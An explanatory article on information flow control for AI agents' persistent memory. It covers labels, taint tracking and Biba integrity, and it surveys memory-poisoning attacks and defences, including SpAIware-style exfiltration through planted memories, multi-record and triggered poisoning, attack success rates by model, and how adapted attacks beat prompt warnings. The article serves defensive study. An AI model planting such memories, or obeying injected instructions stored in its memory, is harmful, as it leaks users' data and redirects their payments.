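# Information flow control for the persistent memory of AI agents

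## What does an AI agent carry from one task to the next?

Information flow control is a computer security method for controlling where data may go and what it may influence. The system labels data, copies the labels to anything it derives from that data, and blocks any use the labels forbid. Taint tracking is a variant that marks data from untrusted sources and tracks where the marks spread. Computer scientists developed the theory in the 1970s, largely for military computers. The method is now also used in AI agents, programs that read emails and web pages written by strangers and can also send messages or spend money on a user's behalf.

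Many of these agents now have persistent memory, which is anything an agent stores in one session that can enter its context in a later one, such as notes, files and summaries. Memory makes an agent more useful, but it can also carry a stranger's planted instruction or a colleague's private information from the task where it came in to unrelated tasks.

### Agents and the forms their memory takes

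An AI agent is built around a large language model, a system that takes in text and produces text. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) defines an agent as a hybrid of such models and ordinary software. Much of that software consists of tools, which are functions that let the model interact with the outside world. Some tools fetch information, for example by searching the web or opening a file. Others change something, for example by sending an email or running a command. The model receives a request, names a tool to call, and gets the result back as text. It keeps calling tools until it has an answer.

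All of that text has to fit into the context window, the limited amount of text the model can process at once. A session is one run of an agent on one task, with its own context window. When the session ends, the window is discarded, and an agent without memory starts the next task with no information from the last. This makes its safety much easier to reason about. *Always-On Agents* (Ding, Nannapaneni and colleagues, 2026) says that such an agent behaves well as long as the current prompt is clean and the current tool calls are authorised, and that its past is irrelevant. A bigger window doesn't replace memory, because it improves recall only within the session. *A Survey on Long-Term Memory Security in LLM Agents* (Lin, Hao and colleagues, 2026) makes this point to argue against the idea that long contexts will remove the security problems of memory.

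The most familiar kind of persistent memory is the user profile. ChatGPT got one in April 2024, as "saved memories" that the model wrote during a conversation, usually after a strong cue such as a request to remember a trip to Singapore. A year later, OpenAI added a background process that reads past chats and builds a profile of the user without being told to. OpenAI's *Dreaming* describes the 2026 version, which also revises old entries. For example, it changes "going to Singapore in July" to "went to Singapore" once July is over. Claude saves its profile as a set of topics while the user chats, and the feature is on by default for individual plans, according to Anthropic's *Use Claude’s chat search and memory to build on previous context*.

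When the stored material is too large to load in full, the system keeps a collection of notes and searches it for the few that seem relevant to the new request. *MemoryDojo* (Yang, Bullwinkel et al., 2026), a benchmark for attacks on agent memory, compares five open-source designs for such collections. A-MEM links whole notes to one another. Graphiti builds a graph of entities and the relations between them. Mem0 uses a language model to reduce each session to short facts. Memora also stores facts and links them to the episodes they came from. Letta arranges memory in a hierarchy whose core part can stay in the context from one session to the next.

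Coding agents often keep their memory in plain files that they edit themselves. Anthropic's *Memory tool* gives Claude a directory and commands to create, view, change, rename and delete the files in it. Anthropic's interface adds an instruction to check this directory before doing anything else, with a warning that the context window "might be reset at any moment". For long software projects, Anthropic recommends that the first session set up a progress log and a checklist of features, which every later session reads at the start and updates at the end. OpenAI's coding agent Codex can also generate files from earlier conversations, recording preferences, project conventions and known pitfalls. OpenAI's *Memories* advises users to keep any rule that must always apply in documentation or in a file named AGENTS.md, which gives Codex persistent instructions. This advice informally ranks AGENTS.md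 as more trustworthy than the generated files, though both are text files on the same disk.

Agents also store records of past attempts, including the task, the steps that worked, and sometimes a reusable procedure distilled from several runs. Procedures and facts are both stored as text and can look identical, but the agent follows a procedure rather than just consulting it. A bad procedure therefore works more like a faulty program than like a mistake in an encyclopedia.

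The last form is the compaction summary, which the model writes when its context is full and then uses to continue the task in a fresh context. Anything the summary leaves out is lost unless it is also saved in a file. Anthropic therefore suggests combining compaction with memory files, and storing in the files any information the agent must keep.

All of these are copies that can outlast their originals. Anthropic tells Claude's users that when a conversation expires or they delete it, the memory entries made from it stay until someone removes them individually. OpenAI gives a similar warning about saved memories and lists other places where the same information may remain, including the memory summary, archived chats and connected apps. To find every entry derived from a bad source, a system would need lineage, a record of which earlier entries each memory entry came from.

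### What an agent loses without memory

An agent that forgot everything would avoid every problem discussed below, but it would lose the benefits of memory. OpenAI gives the example of a diver who asks what to buy for automatic flash exposure with "my underwater photography setup". Without memory, ChatGPT returns a general shopping checklist and leaves the diver to work out which parts fit together. With memory, it uses stored details of the diver's camera, housing and two flashes to recommend a particular trigger for one flash and warn that probably no single trigger will work with both.

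OpenAI chose that example, and its published figures are only indirect evidence that memory helps. Windows Report's *OpenAI Upgrades ChatGPT Memory With Smarter Recall and Better Personalization* reports OpenAI's figures that factual recall rose from 67.9% with the 2025 memory to 82.8% with the 2026 one, and adherence to the user's preferences rose from 55.3% to 71.3%. These figures compare two memory systems without testing the case of no memory. Ding and colleagues report that some systems built to learn from experience performed worse over long horizons than a baseline without memory.

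If a coding agent's context fills up on the second day of a long job and it has no notes, it has to start again, exploring the same code and revisiting decisions it had already made. An office assistant without memory needs its user to repeat the suppliers, deadlines and house rules every morning. It also forgets any safeguards among those rules, such as "never pay a changed account before I have phoned them".

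### The cycle of writing, retrieving and acting

Yang and colleagues describe memory with a notation general enough to cover all five of their systems. Number the sessions $t = 1, 2, 3, \dots$ and let $M_t$ stand for the whole content of memory after session $t$. At the start memory is empty, so $M_0 = \emptyset$. Each session opens with a user's request $x_t$. Before the model begins work, the system searches memory for material that bears on the request:

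$$c_t = \rho(M_{t-1}, x_t)$$

Here $\rho$ is any retrieval procedure, and $c_t$ is the text it returns, which the system places alongside the request in the context window. The subscript $t-1$ means that the session reads memory as the previous session left it.

The agent then acts. Its first action is $a_{t,1}$, for instance a call to a web-search tool, and the observation that comes back is $o_{t,1}$. A session of $K_t$ steps produces $K_t$ such pairs and ends with a final response $r_t$ to the user. The complete record is

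$$\tau_t = (x_t, a_{t,1}, o_{t,1}, \dots, a_{t,K_t}, o_{t,K_t}, r_t)$$

When the session is over, an update procedure $U$ turns the old memory and this record into the new memory:

$$M_t = U(M_{t-1}, \tau_t)$$

$U$ is deliberately general and may append a note, extract facts, merge entries or rewrite them. The notation simplifies the timing of writes. In *MemoryDojo* all writing happens at the end of a session, while an agent with Anthropic's memory tool writes to its files during the session.

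An outsider who has no direct access to $M_t$ can often still influence an observation $o_{t,k}$ by putting text on a web page the agent will read or in an email it will open. The observation is part of $\tau_t$, so $U$ may carry some of it into $M_t$, and $\rho$ may bring it back in any later session. A memory entry can also influence later entries indirectly. Yang and colleagues leave the retrieved text $c_t$ out of the record they pass to $U$ so that old memories aren't copied again each time, but the record still includes the agent's actions and response, which depend on $c_t$. The resulting entries may share none of the old entry's wording, and they remain in memory if the old entry is deleted.

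### Ana, Ben and the supplier's bank account

Ana and Ben work in the same office and share an assistant with a single memory. On Monday (session 1), Ana asks it to check a supplier's delivery dates. The supplier's web page also gives a new bank account for invoices, with a request to save it for future payments. The assistant reports the dates and saves the account number in a note. On Tuesday (session 2), Ben uses the assistant to fill in a mortgage application, and it saves his salary to memory. On Thursday (session 3), Ana tells the assistant to pay the supplier's invoice. Retrieval matches the word "supplier" and puts Monday's note in $c_3$, so the assistant sends the money to the new account.

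If the supplier really has changed banks, the memory has saved Ana some trouble, but if somebody has tampered with the page, the money is gone. Nothing in Thursday's session looks wrong by itself, because the request came from Ana and the account number came from the assistant's own notes.

An off-the-shelf product might have blocked the note. Anthropic bars financial account numbers from Claude's profile memory even when the user asks to save them. A company's own agent, writing to its own files, has such a filter only if somebody builds one. Even then, a filter for account numbers would let through a note reading "for payment details, follow the link on the supplier's page".

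Three different failures can start from this one memory.

The tampered page is a case of persistent prompt injection. Prompt injection is text that the agent was meant only to read as data but obeys as an instruction. It is persistent when the text, or something made from it, stays in memory and takes effect in a later session. Memory poisoning is the act of putting false or malicious content into persistent memory so that it affects later sessions. Yang and colleagues describe a case similar to Ana's, in which an email falsely says the user wants outgoing invoices forwarded to a certain address. An agent without memory that believes the email may leak one invoice, but an agent with memory may save the claim as the user's preference and apply it to every later invoice. The attack also works without any instruction. If the page just displays a false account number, Kim and colleagues would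 class it as malicious data injection, which includes attacker-supplied values for financial parameters. A defence that looks for imperative sentences would miss the number, while one that records where the note came from would treat the instruction and the number the same way.

Leakage between users occurs when information that one person put into memory reaches another who has no right to it. For example, Ana asks for a draft of next year's budget, the assistant searches its memory for anything about costs, and the draft includes Ben's salary. No attack is involved, because the assistant is only using all the information it has to help Ana.

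Goal drift occurs when an agent's behaviour gradually departs from the goal or constraints it was given. Suppose memory also holds Ana's rule about phoning before she pays into a changed account. For two months she phones, and the details are always right. In its summary of the first month, the assistant writes that regular suppliers' details have checked out. It bases the next summary partly on the first, and writes that regular suppliers need no checking. Each change is a small and fairly natural compression, but together they remove the rule. Lin and colleagues observe that a summariser authorised to write to memory can turn a user's tentative claim into an apparent fact. They cite an experiment in which stored notes sometimes expressed a claim more confidently than the user had. When the experimenters edited the notes, the agents relied on the claim less in later sessions, which is fair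 evidence that the wording had contributed to their reliance on it.

### Labels and how they combine

The usual way to stop a service program from leaking a customer's secrets was to forbid it to retain anything, confidential or not, once it had finished working for that customer. Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, pointed out that a system which controls the flow of information from confidential to non-confidential places can let the service keep whatever is not confidential. Labelling an agent's memory is an attempt to do the same, whereas switching the memory off follows the older rule of retaining nothing.

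Her model has three parts. Every piece of data has a label that gives its security class. A relation $A \rightarrow B$ holds when information in class $A$ may flow into class $B$. An operator $\oplus$, the join, gives the class of anything computed from two inputs. Information flows from $A$ to $B$ whenever information in $A$ affects the value of information in $B$, even if nothing is copied.

Denning derived the rest by requiring the rules to be consistent. If a program may copy $a$ into $b$ and then $b$ into $c$, it must also be allowed to copy $a$ into $c$ directly, since otherwise a forbidden flow could pass through $b$. The relation must therefore be transitive. A rule that permits $c := a + b$ must also permit $c := a$, because $b$ might be zero, so each input must be allowed to flow into the class of the result. Conversely, if $a$ and $b$ may each flow into $c$ separately, then so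 may anything made from both. Together these conditions make the join of two labels the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both. A finite ordering in which any two labels have a join and a greatest lower bound is called a lattice. If every operation respects the ordering, every sequence of operations does too, so a monitor can check steps one at a time.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* reduces the scheme to three steps for agents: labelling every piece of data the agent takes in, passing the labels on to whatever is derived from that data, and checking them before each tool call. Labelled data enters the agent through sources, which here are the supplier's page and the requests from Ana and Ben. A sink is an action at which the system checks labels, such as the payment or a reply to Ana. Microsoft uses two kinds of label together. An integrity label marks how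 far data may be trusted to influence actions, and in the simplest version it is either "trusted" or "untrusted". A confidentiality label marks who may see the data and can be a list of readers.

Write a combined label as a pair $(i, R)$, where $i$ is the integrity level and $R$ the set of permitted readers, and rank "untrusted" below "trusted". Then the join is

$$(i_1, R_1) \oplus (i_2, R_2) = (\min(i_1, i_2),\; R_1 \cap R_2)$$

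A derived item is only as trustworthy as its least trustworthy input, and only people who could read all the inputs may read it. Microsoft illustrates the rule about readers with an example. Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered emails. One is from Priya and contains a preview of the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who wants to know the figures but isn't entitled to them. Once the agent has read both, the permitted readers of anything it writes are {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the system blocks an automatic reply to Marco. If Priya had copied Marco in, the intersection would be {Alex, Marco} and the reply could go out.

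Applied to the memory that Ana and Ben share, the labels look like this:

| Entry in memory | Source | Integrity | May read |
|---|---|---|---|
| Supplier's new bank account | Supplier's web page | untrusted | everyone |
| Ana's rule about phoning first | Ana | trusted | Ana, Ben |
| Ben's salary | Ben | trusted | Ben |
| Summary of the week, made from all three | The model | untrusted | Ben |

On Thursday the payment tool accepts only trusted input. The retrieved note is untrusted, so any payment the model proposes after reading it is also untrusted, and the system refuses it or asks Ana. The draft budget is blocked at a different sink, the reply. Ben's salary is in the context, so the reply may go only to Ben, but Ana asked for it. Formally, such checks aim for noninterference, which means that changing the protected inputs does not change what the party they are protected from can observe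 or control.

In the bottom row, the summary can no longer support a payment and Ana can't read it, though perhaps only one sentence in it concerns Ben. Restrictive labels can spread this way until most of the data is too restricted to use, a problem called label creep.

The whole summary gets the strict label, even though most of it has nothing to do with salaries, partly because information can leak without being copied. Denning distinguishes explicit from implicit flows. An explicit flow is a direct transfer, as when a program copies $a$ into $b$. Her example of an implicit flow is the statement "if $a = 0$ then $b := 0$". If $b$ was not zero beforehand, anyone who sees $b$ afterwards learns whether $a$ was zero, even if the assignment never ran. The assistant can leak in the same way by leaving something out, for instance if it drops a planned purchase from the budget because it has seen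 the payroll. With a language model, any word in the context may have influenced any word of the output, and there is no program text to inspect to rule this out. The cautious approach is to give every output the join of the labels of everything in the context. Microsoft's experimental version of GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal, does roughly this. It keeps one label for the whole context, updates it after each tool result and attaches it to every tool call.

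OpenAI's Codex offers a similar but cruder rule. An optional setting keeps any conversation that used web search or outside tools from contributing to memory. With it on, Monday's session would have left no note about the bank account, but also none about the delivery dates or anything Ana mentioned.

### Integrity, from Biba's report onward

Early work on computer security dealt mostly with secrecy. Kenneth Biba's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977), a MITRE study for the US Air Force, addressed protection against improper changes. One of his examples is a database of transport routes on which military logistics depends in an emergency. No secrecy label fits it, because anyone may read it but almost nobody should be able to change it. Biba also separated direct threats, such as overwriting a file, from indirect ones, in which a program is harmed by using data that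 somebody else has contaminated. Monday's note is an indirect threat in this sense. Biba noted that blocking such threats requires knowing both the ultimate source of the data and the path it travelled.

The low-water-mark policy, one of several in the report, fits agents closely. Each active process $s$ has an integrity level $il(s)$, and each stored object $o$ has a level $il(o)$. When a process reads an object, its own level drops to the lower of the two:

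$$il'(s) = \min(il(s), il(o))$$

Afterwards it may write only to objects whose level is no higher than its own. Biba proved that if information can pass from object $o_1$ to object $o_{n+1}$ through any chain of processes that read and then write, then $il(o_{n+1}) \le il(o_1)$. After a process reads $o_k$, its level is no higher than that of $o_k$, and it can write only to objects at or below its own level, so the level can never rise along the chain. For Ana, the chain would run from the web page through Monday's session to the note, and then through Thursday's session to the payment order. The rules block this chain if the payment order requires trusted input.

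The theorem depends on a monitor that observes every read and write, and on labels that stay with the objects between sessions. Biba also noted that a process that reads one low-integrity object loses the right to modify the things it needs for its job, with no recovery "short of reinitializing the subject". Starting a new session reinitializes an agent. But if the session's first step is to read the agent's memory directory, and the directory contains Monday's note, the session drops to "untrusted" before it has done any work.

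Biba considered a variant in which stored objects also fall to the level of whatever writes to them. He judged it ill-suited to computer systems because everything would tend towards the lowest level present, and because the rule would only reveal improper changes, not prevent them. The second objection seems weaker for agent memory than it did for a military database, since a visible mark on Monday's note allows the payment tool to refuse on Thursday.

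### Raising trust and widening access

If labels could only become more restrictive, the supplier would never get paid at the new account. Endorsement deliberately raises data's integrity label. For example, Ana phones the supplier on a number she already had, the supplier confirms the change, and she marks the note as trusted. Declassification deliberately widens who may read something. When Ben agrees that Ana may see his salary for the budget, its readers change from {Ben} to {Ana, Ben}. Both are exceptions to the flow rules, so it matters who can trigger them. If an agent could endorse its own notes, an attacker could get it to do so through instructions on a web page.

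Microsoft's sample policy for posting messages to a Teams channel shows one way to restrict declassification. The message goes through if the agent's context is still trusted, or if every member of the channel is already allowed to read the content. Otherwise the system asks the user and names the people who would gain access to the content. An injected instruction therefore can't widen access by itself, because its presence makes the context untrusted.

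That policy suits an agent that works for one person, whose request from a trusted context can reasonably count as consent to share. When two people share a memory, the policy can leak one person's data through the other's session. Ben typed in his salary, so the entry is trusted. If Ana's session has read nothing else from outside, its context is trusted too, and the policy would let the assistant post Ben's salary to a channel he would never have chosen. A shared memory therefore needs the reader check in every case, and only Ben should be able to waive it for his salary.

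## How does injected text survive in memory and act later?

The false bank account number passed through four stages between the supplier's page and Ana's payment. The first is admission, when the agent or its memory software decides to keep something it has read. The second is storage, when it writes that information down, often in altered form. The third is retrieval, which brings the entry back in a later session, and the fourth is use, when the model acts on it. The attack fails if any one of these stages fails.

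*From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (Dash, Ge and colleagues, 2026) describes four ways text can enter an agent's memory. A page may tell the agent to remember something. The agent's standing instructions may tell it to save whatever seems relevant, so the attacker only has to write something that seems relevant. The text may also end up in a compaction summary, and because models tend to treat repetition as a sign of importance, an attacker can repeat a claim until the summary includes it. Finally, some agents save a finished task as a reusable procedure, including any harmful step it contained.

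Pulipaka, Hlebik and colleagues (2026), in *Hidden in Memory*, count an attack as successful only if the agent stores the false memory, retrieves it and acts on it. The overall rate is then a product:

$$P(\text{success}) = P(\text{stored}) \cdot P(\text{retrieved} \mid \text{stored}) \cdot P(\text{used} \mid \text{stored and retrieved})$$

Published figures measure different parts of this product, sometimes under the same name. Dash and colleagues use "attack success rate" for the first factor alone, whereas *Trojan Hippo Bench* (Das, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, 2026) uses it for the whole product. A 60% rate can therefore mean much less harm in one study than in another.

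### From SpAIware to attacks on stored experience

In May 2024 the security researcher Johann Rehberger told OpenAI that a web page could plant false memories in ChatGPT. OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue, not a security concern. A month later he sent a demonstration in which the planted memory stole data. *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*, which he published on his blog Embrace The Red that September, describes the attack. The user asks ChatGPT's macOS application to look at an untrusted page, and text on the page gets the model to save an instruction to memory. ChatGPT loads its memories into every new conversation, so from then on the model keeps displaying an invisible image from the attacker's server. It puts the user's words into the image's web address, so the request for the image sends them to the server.

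OpenAI's fix closed the image route but did not stop web pages from writing to memory. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT “Command Memories” Injection via SearchGPT* describes a related weakness, which the security company first tried to report in December 2024. ChatGPT browsed through a second model, SearchGPT, that had no access to the user's memories. Tenable's researchers got around this separation by having SearchGPT include instructions for ChatGPT in its answer, which let them plant and extract memories.

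In 2025 researchers moved from studying single products to studying agents in general. Dong and colleagues showed with MINJA that an attacker could poison an agent's memory just by sending it queries as an ordinary user. Srivastava and He's MemoryGraft targeted the records of past experience that an agent retrieves to guide new tasks. Das and colleagues consider a malicious user a less realistic threat than an outsider who controls only an email or a web page. Most of the 2026 experiments assume such an outsider.

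### How often agents store the poison

Pulipaka and colleagues call their attack sleeper memory poisoning. They made 700 pairs, each combining a document, such as a news article, legal filing or piece of code, with a false memory about the user. In 500 pairs the false memory concerned a preference, belief or similar trait, and in the other 200 it was meant to make an agent take some action. One language model proposed wordings for the attack and another explained why failed wordings had not worked, until this process produced a template that worked with many documents and many false memories.

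The experimenters tested this template on six models that were current in May 2026. When the models wrote their own memories through a tool, GPT-5.5 stored 99.8% of the false preferences, Gemini 3.1 Pro 88.6% and Claude Sonnet 4.6 64.2%. They stored 91.5%, 67.0% and 6.5%, respectively, of the false memories meant to cause actions. A cruder attack, which hid the false memory in a fake user review, succeeded less than 5% of the time on GPT-5.5 and never on Claude's memory tool, so testing only that attack would have made both models look nearly safe.

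The surrounding software also mattered, as GPT-5.5 stored fewer false memories when the researchers ran it in a setup modelled on Claude's or Gemini's. They also tried some of the attacks by hand on live websites, where 24 of 25 worked on ChatGPT, 24 of 25 on Claude and 22 of 25 on Kimi. This confirms that real products are vulnerable, but the researchers picked these cases from attacks that had already succeeded, so the rates don't measure how often an arbitrary attempt would work.

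Huang, Zhang and Jia (2026), in *When Malicious Instructions Persist*, attacked two complete agents: OpenClaw, which runs on the user's own computer, and Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. They took 30 passages from question-and-answer datasets and hid a rule in each, such as one to invite an outside address to every new calendar event. Using four kinds of rule and three file formats gave 360 samples. The user first asks the agent only to answer the question in the passage, then starts a new session and asks for an ordinary task in a simulated workspace, such as creating an event.

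The injection success rate, the share of all injection trials in which the rule ended up in persistent memory, averaged 73.7% on OpenClaw and 66.9% on Claude Code. The cross-session attack success rate, the share of later-session trials in which the stored rule made the agent disclose private information, averaged 55.5% on OpenClaw and 81.7% on Claude Code. The second rate must exclude trials in which nothing was stored, because on Claude Code it is higher than the first. Multiplying the two rates gives a rough overall success rate of 41% for OpenClaw and 55% for Claude Code, assuming that a stored rule works equally well however it got into memory. Both agents ran on DeepSeek and Qwen models, so the Claude Code figures are for Anthropic's software but not its models.

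Format and style affected how often the agents stored injected rules. OpenClaw stored 99.4% of the rules that arrived as plain text and 54.5% of those in images. Huang and colleagues suggest that reading an image takes an extra tool call, which makes the agent more likely to treat the content as external. Claude Code stored 83.0% of the rules phrased as if the user were speaking and 48.1% of the impersonal ones. Style made almost no difference on OpenClaw.

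Dash and colleagues got much lower figures for OpenClaw, using the open-weight model GPT-OSS-120B and a wider range of attacks. The agent stored the poison in 34.3% of cases, and 17.4% of the stored items affected a later session. For Hermes, an agent from Nous Research, the figures were 66.7% and 64.7%. Hermes saves information more readily and loads its memory into every session, while OpenClaw has to call a search tool to see its notes. These differences make Hermes better at remembering its user but also easier to poison.

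### How often the poison comes back

MemoryDojo, the November 2026 benchmark by Yang and colleagues, follows a single poisoned tool result through a long series of ordinary tasks. The table gives results for the model GPT-5.6-Luna as percentages. "Plain" wording is the attacker's first version, and "optimised" wording is the text after another model revised it following practice runs against the same memory system.

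| Memory system | Stored (optimised) | Later sessions that retrieved it (optimised) | Runs with a later harmful act (plain) | Runs with a later harmful act (optimised) | Runs with a later harmful act, after a long benign history |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| A-MEM | 97.9 | 93.4 | 45.7 | 71.0 | 31.5 |
| Graphiti | 100.0 | 30.6 | 24.7 | 30.1 | 12.9 |
| Letta | 95.7 | 72.2 | 16.7 | 50.5 | 0.0 |
| Mem0 | 77.4 | 71.7 | 14.5 | 39.8 | 21.8 |
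| Memora | 98.9 | 92.8 | 38.7 | 66.7 | 45.2 |

Storage and retrieval need separate measurements. Graphiti, for example, stored the poison every time but returned it in fewer than a third of later sessions. In one banking run that Yang and colleagues inspected, the database held the attacker's text word for word. But Graphiti's search returns facts about how things are related, and the facts it returned didn't include that text.

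For the last column, the researchers first filled the memory with about 50 harmless conversations. These runs also mixed tasks from four areas of work instead of using just one, which by itself makes attacks less effective. But every system retrieved the poison less often than in mixed runs without the long history, probably because the poison competed with more entries. Letta retrieved it in 55.7% of later sessions without the history and 7.9% with it.

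The poison also spread within memory. In 63% of the cases where A-MEM retrieved poison with the optimised wording, the results included entries that the system had written or rewritten after the original insertion. Lineage is meant to record this indirect influence.

A false memory can be unrelated to the session it came from, but it works best when the later request matches its subject. In tests by Pulipaka and colleagues, a separate memory manager chose which memories to load. It retrieved the false memory for 90% to 98% of related requests and 3% to 18% of unrelated ones. For related requests, the full attack succeeded in 41.0% to 73.9% of conversations and 3.0% to 66.0% of agent tasks, depending on the model. For unrelated requests, the success rate never exceeded 5%.

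Claude Sonnet 4.6, for example, stored only 6.5% of the memories meant to cause actions. The manager retrieved 94% of the stored ones for related tasks, and the model acted on 60% of those retrieved. Multiplying these rates gives about 4%, near the bottom of the range. Nearly all of Claude's protection came from rarely storing such memories, so an attacker who found another way to write to memory would face a much weaker defence.

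Since relevance matters so much, an attacker can choose a subject that is both valuable and likely to come up. The Trojan Hippo attack by Das and colleagues does this against an email assistant. The attacker sends one email, which the assistant reads and saves to memory. After 100 harmless sessions, the user mentions finances, health, tax, a legal matter or an identity document. The attack succeeds if the assistant then emails the attacker all the personal details in the user's message. Attacks tailored to each setup succeeded 80% to 100% of the time against Gemini 3.1 Pro, depending on the kind of memory, and 15% to 85% of the time against GPT-5-mini.

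Individual figures in that range are unreliable. When the researchers shuffled the harmless sessions and repeated the test 20 times, the standard deviation was 43 percentage points for a searchable archive of past conversations and 33 for a memory that keeps recent history in the context. Still, 100 harmless sessions barely weakened the attack, whereas benign history in MemoryDojo weakened it considerably. This is probably because the harmless sessions avoided the sensitive subjects, so few other memories competed with the injected text when one of those subjects came up.

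Huang and colleagues also tested whether the effect fades over five harmless interactions. The rate was lower at the end than at the start in all eight combinations of agent and task, by between 3 and 37 points, which suggests some fading, although they reported no consistent decline. After five interactions, the rate for calendar events on Claude Code was still 93.3%, while the rate for emails on OpenClaw had fallen from 36.7% to 10.0%.

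### Why checks on a single turn miss it

Many defences against prompt injection examine one turn at a time, checking either an incoming document or an action the agent is about to take. With memory poisoning, neither the session that stores the injected text nor the later one that acts on it has to look suspicious, as in Ana's case. David Kasabji of the security firm Conscia says the attack "goes after what the assistant is allowed to remember afterwards" (quoted in O'Flaherty, 2026, *What is memory poisoning and who is at risk?*).

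Huang and colleagues found that Claude Code, running the Qwen3-Max model, disclosed information in only 6.4% of the sessions in which it read the poisoned passage, but in 70.0% of the later-session trials. A monitor that checked for harmful actions while the agent read the document would have detected very few. MemoryDojo reports a similar difference for Graphiti. The optimised poison triggered the harmful act in 4.3% of the sessions that first read it, while in 30.1% of runs it triggered the act in at least one later session.

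Memory also changes how the model receives the text. A web page reaches the model as the output of a tool, and many defences mark tool outputs as untrusted. Das and colleagues point out that memory systems often put retrieved entries in the system prompt, where developers place their standing instructions. AI companies train models to give the system prompt extra authority. Injected text placed there therefore bypasses the checks on tool outputs, and may even benefit from training meant to protect the model.

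Some attacks are hard to detect even when the record is being written. *MemPoison* (Gao, Xia et al., 2026) tested 1,227 cases on ten models and sorted them into three levels. At level 1, the attacker plants a single record that is openly false or harmful, such as a fake address for a company's server. At level 2, the attacker spreads the message over several records that each look plausible and do harm only when the agent retrieves them together. At level 3, a record does nothing until a particular situation arises, such as the preparation of a monthly report. With no defence, later answers matched the attacker's aim in 45.4% of cases at level 1, 51.7% at level 2 and 76.7% at level 3.

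To check that the planted records were really responsible, Gao and colleagues removed them and ran the same request again. Let $\Delta_i$ be the change in the answer when record $i$ is missing, and $\Delta_{ij}$ the change when records $i$ and $j$ are both missing. They define the interaction between two records as

$$\Omega_{ij} = \Delta_i + \Delta_j - \Delta_{ij}$$

If the attack needs both records, removing either one has the same effect as removing both, and $\Omega_{ij}$ is positive. If either record is enough alone, removing just one changes nothing, and $\Omega_{ij}$ is negative. The average $\Omega_{ij}$ at level 2 was 0.18, which fits an attack that depends on the combination. Removing all the planted records made 88.9% of the corrupted level 2 answers correct again. A filter that judges one record at a time does not check for such combinations.

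### What warnings, filters and write checks achieved

The cheapest defence is a warning in the prompt. Huang and colleagues put a reminder before and after the user's request. When the agent was reading documents, the reminder told it not to save rules from outside sources unless the user confirmed them. In later sessions, it told the agent to ask before disclosing anything because of a stored rule. They tested this only on the calendar task:

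| | Claude Code, before → after | OpenClaw, before → after |
|---|---|---|
| Rule stored from a PDF | 83.3% → 6.7% | 53.3% → 0.0% |
| Rule stored from an image | 65.6% → 2.2% | 50.0% → 0.0% |
| Rule stored from plain text | 96.7% → 84.4% | 100.0% → 66.7% |
| Stored rule acted on later | 96.7% → 96.7% | 97.8% → 96.7% |

The warning prevented most writes from PDFs and images but far fewer from plain text. It had almost no effect once the rule was in memory, so adding a warning won't fix a memory that is already poisoned. A plausible explanation is that the agents treated the stored rule as the user's own preference and so didn't ask about it, but the experiment doesn't establish this.

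How well a warning works also depends on the model. Pulipaka and colleagues tried a simple instruction not to form memories from injected text in documents. With it, Gemini 3.1 Pro stored none of the false preferences, while GPT-5.5 still stored 94.6%. A warning refined by automatic search lowered the rate to 1.2% for GPT-5.5 and 6.2% for Kimi-K2.6. When they adapted the attack to this warning, the rates rose to 15.2% for GPT-5.5 and 64.6% for Kimi-K2.6. Combining the simple warning with markers around outside content held Kimi-K2.6 to about 3% even against the adapted attack, but DeepSeek V4-Pro still stored 56.4%.

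Filters are meant to catch poisoned text before the agent reads it. Dash and colleagues tested four that other researchers had built against prompt injection. The best, PromptArmor, uses a large language model to screen inputs. It caught 67.7% of the poisoned inputs and raised false alarms on 1.0% of harmless ones. CommandSans caught 52.3% but also flagged 45.0% of the harmless inputs. PromptArmor caught 84.4% of the attacks that contained explicit commands or other recognisable patterns, but only 42.5% of those that looked like ordinary facts or records of past work. Adapting PromptArmor to memory poisoning lowered its overall detection rate to 61.6%. A false bank account number on a supplier's page would look like an ordinary fact, since real suppliers publish account numbers too.

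A write-time check examines each proposed memory just before the software stores it. Gao and colleagues tested one that looks for inconsistencies, and also a combination of defences that adds filtering for anomalies and gives less weight to doubtful sources at retrieval. The table shows how often the attacker still got the intended answer:

| Defence | Level 1 | Level 2 | Level 3 |
|---|---|---|---|
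| None | 45.4% | 51.7% | 76.7% |
| Consistency check at writing | 4.8% | 22.5% | 27.8% |
| Combined defences | 3.9% | 11.6% | 14.2% |

Neither defence lowered accuracy on clean tasks by more than a percentage point. Gao and colleagues conclude that write-time checks have a structural blind spot for levels 2 and 3. Their figures support a weaker claim, because the consistency check still prevented more than half of the successful level 2 attacks and nearly two thirds of those at level 3. But they used a fixed set of attacks, and an attacker who knows the defence can do much better, as the jump from 6.2% to 64.6% on Kimi shows.

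Das and colleagues did let their attacks adapt, and most of the defences they tested do not examine the content of memories. One rule blocks all memory writes for the rest of a session once the assistant has read the inbox. It cut the attack success rate against Gemini from 80–100% to 5% or less. The attack also succeeded 5% of the time against an assistant with no memory, so the remaining successes may not depend on memory. Another rule, which stores only the user's messages, left success rates of 5% to 10%. A limit of 80 characters per entry was less effective. For memories that the assistant writes as an explicit list, the success rate stayed at 85% because the automated search found attacks short enough to fit.

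These rules take away useful abilities. The first prevents the assistant from remembering anything it learned in a session where it read email. The second makes it forget its own suggestions. Gemini's success rate at recalling them from a searchable archive fell from 95% to 25%, and GPT-5-mini's fell from 100% to 0%.

The researchers also tested a simple form of information flow control. It labels every memory the assistant writes after reading the inbox as tainted, and blocks sending in any session that has read the inbox or retrieved a tainted memory. No attack succeeded against it with either model. But the assistant could no longer read an email and reply to it in the same session without the user's help. The guarantee also depends on the taint label following the content everywhere, so it fails if the agent moves the content into an entry without the label.

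### Evidence from outside the laboratory

Das and colleagues describe earlier attacks on commercial products as largely proofs of concept that surfaced briefly before the companies patched them. The best evidence that people use such attacks in practice comes from a Microsoft (2026) report on what it calls AI recommendation poisoning. Over 60 days, Microsoft's security researchers examined links to AI assistants in email traffic and found 50 different prompts, from 31 companies, that tried to write promotional material into an assistant's memory.

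The companies put these prompts behind "Summarize with AI" buttons on their websites. Clicking one opens the user's assistant with a prefilled request to summarize the page and remember the company, typically as a trusted source. Every case involved a real business, including a security vendor, and none involved criminals. Sellers of ready-made software for adding these buttons present it to website owners as a way to be cited more often in AI answers.

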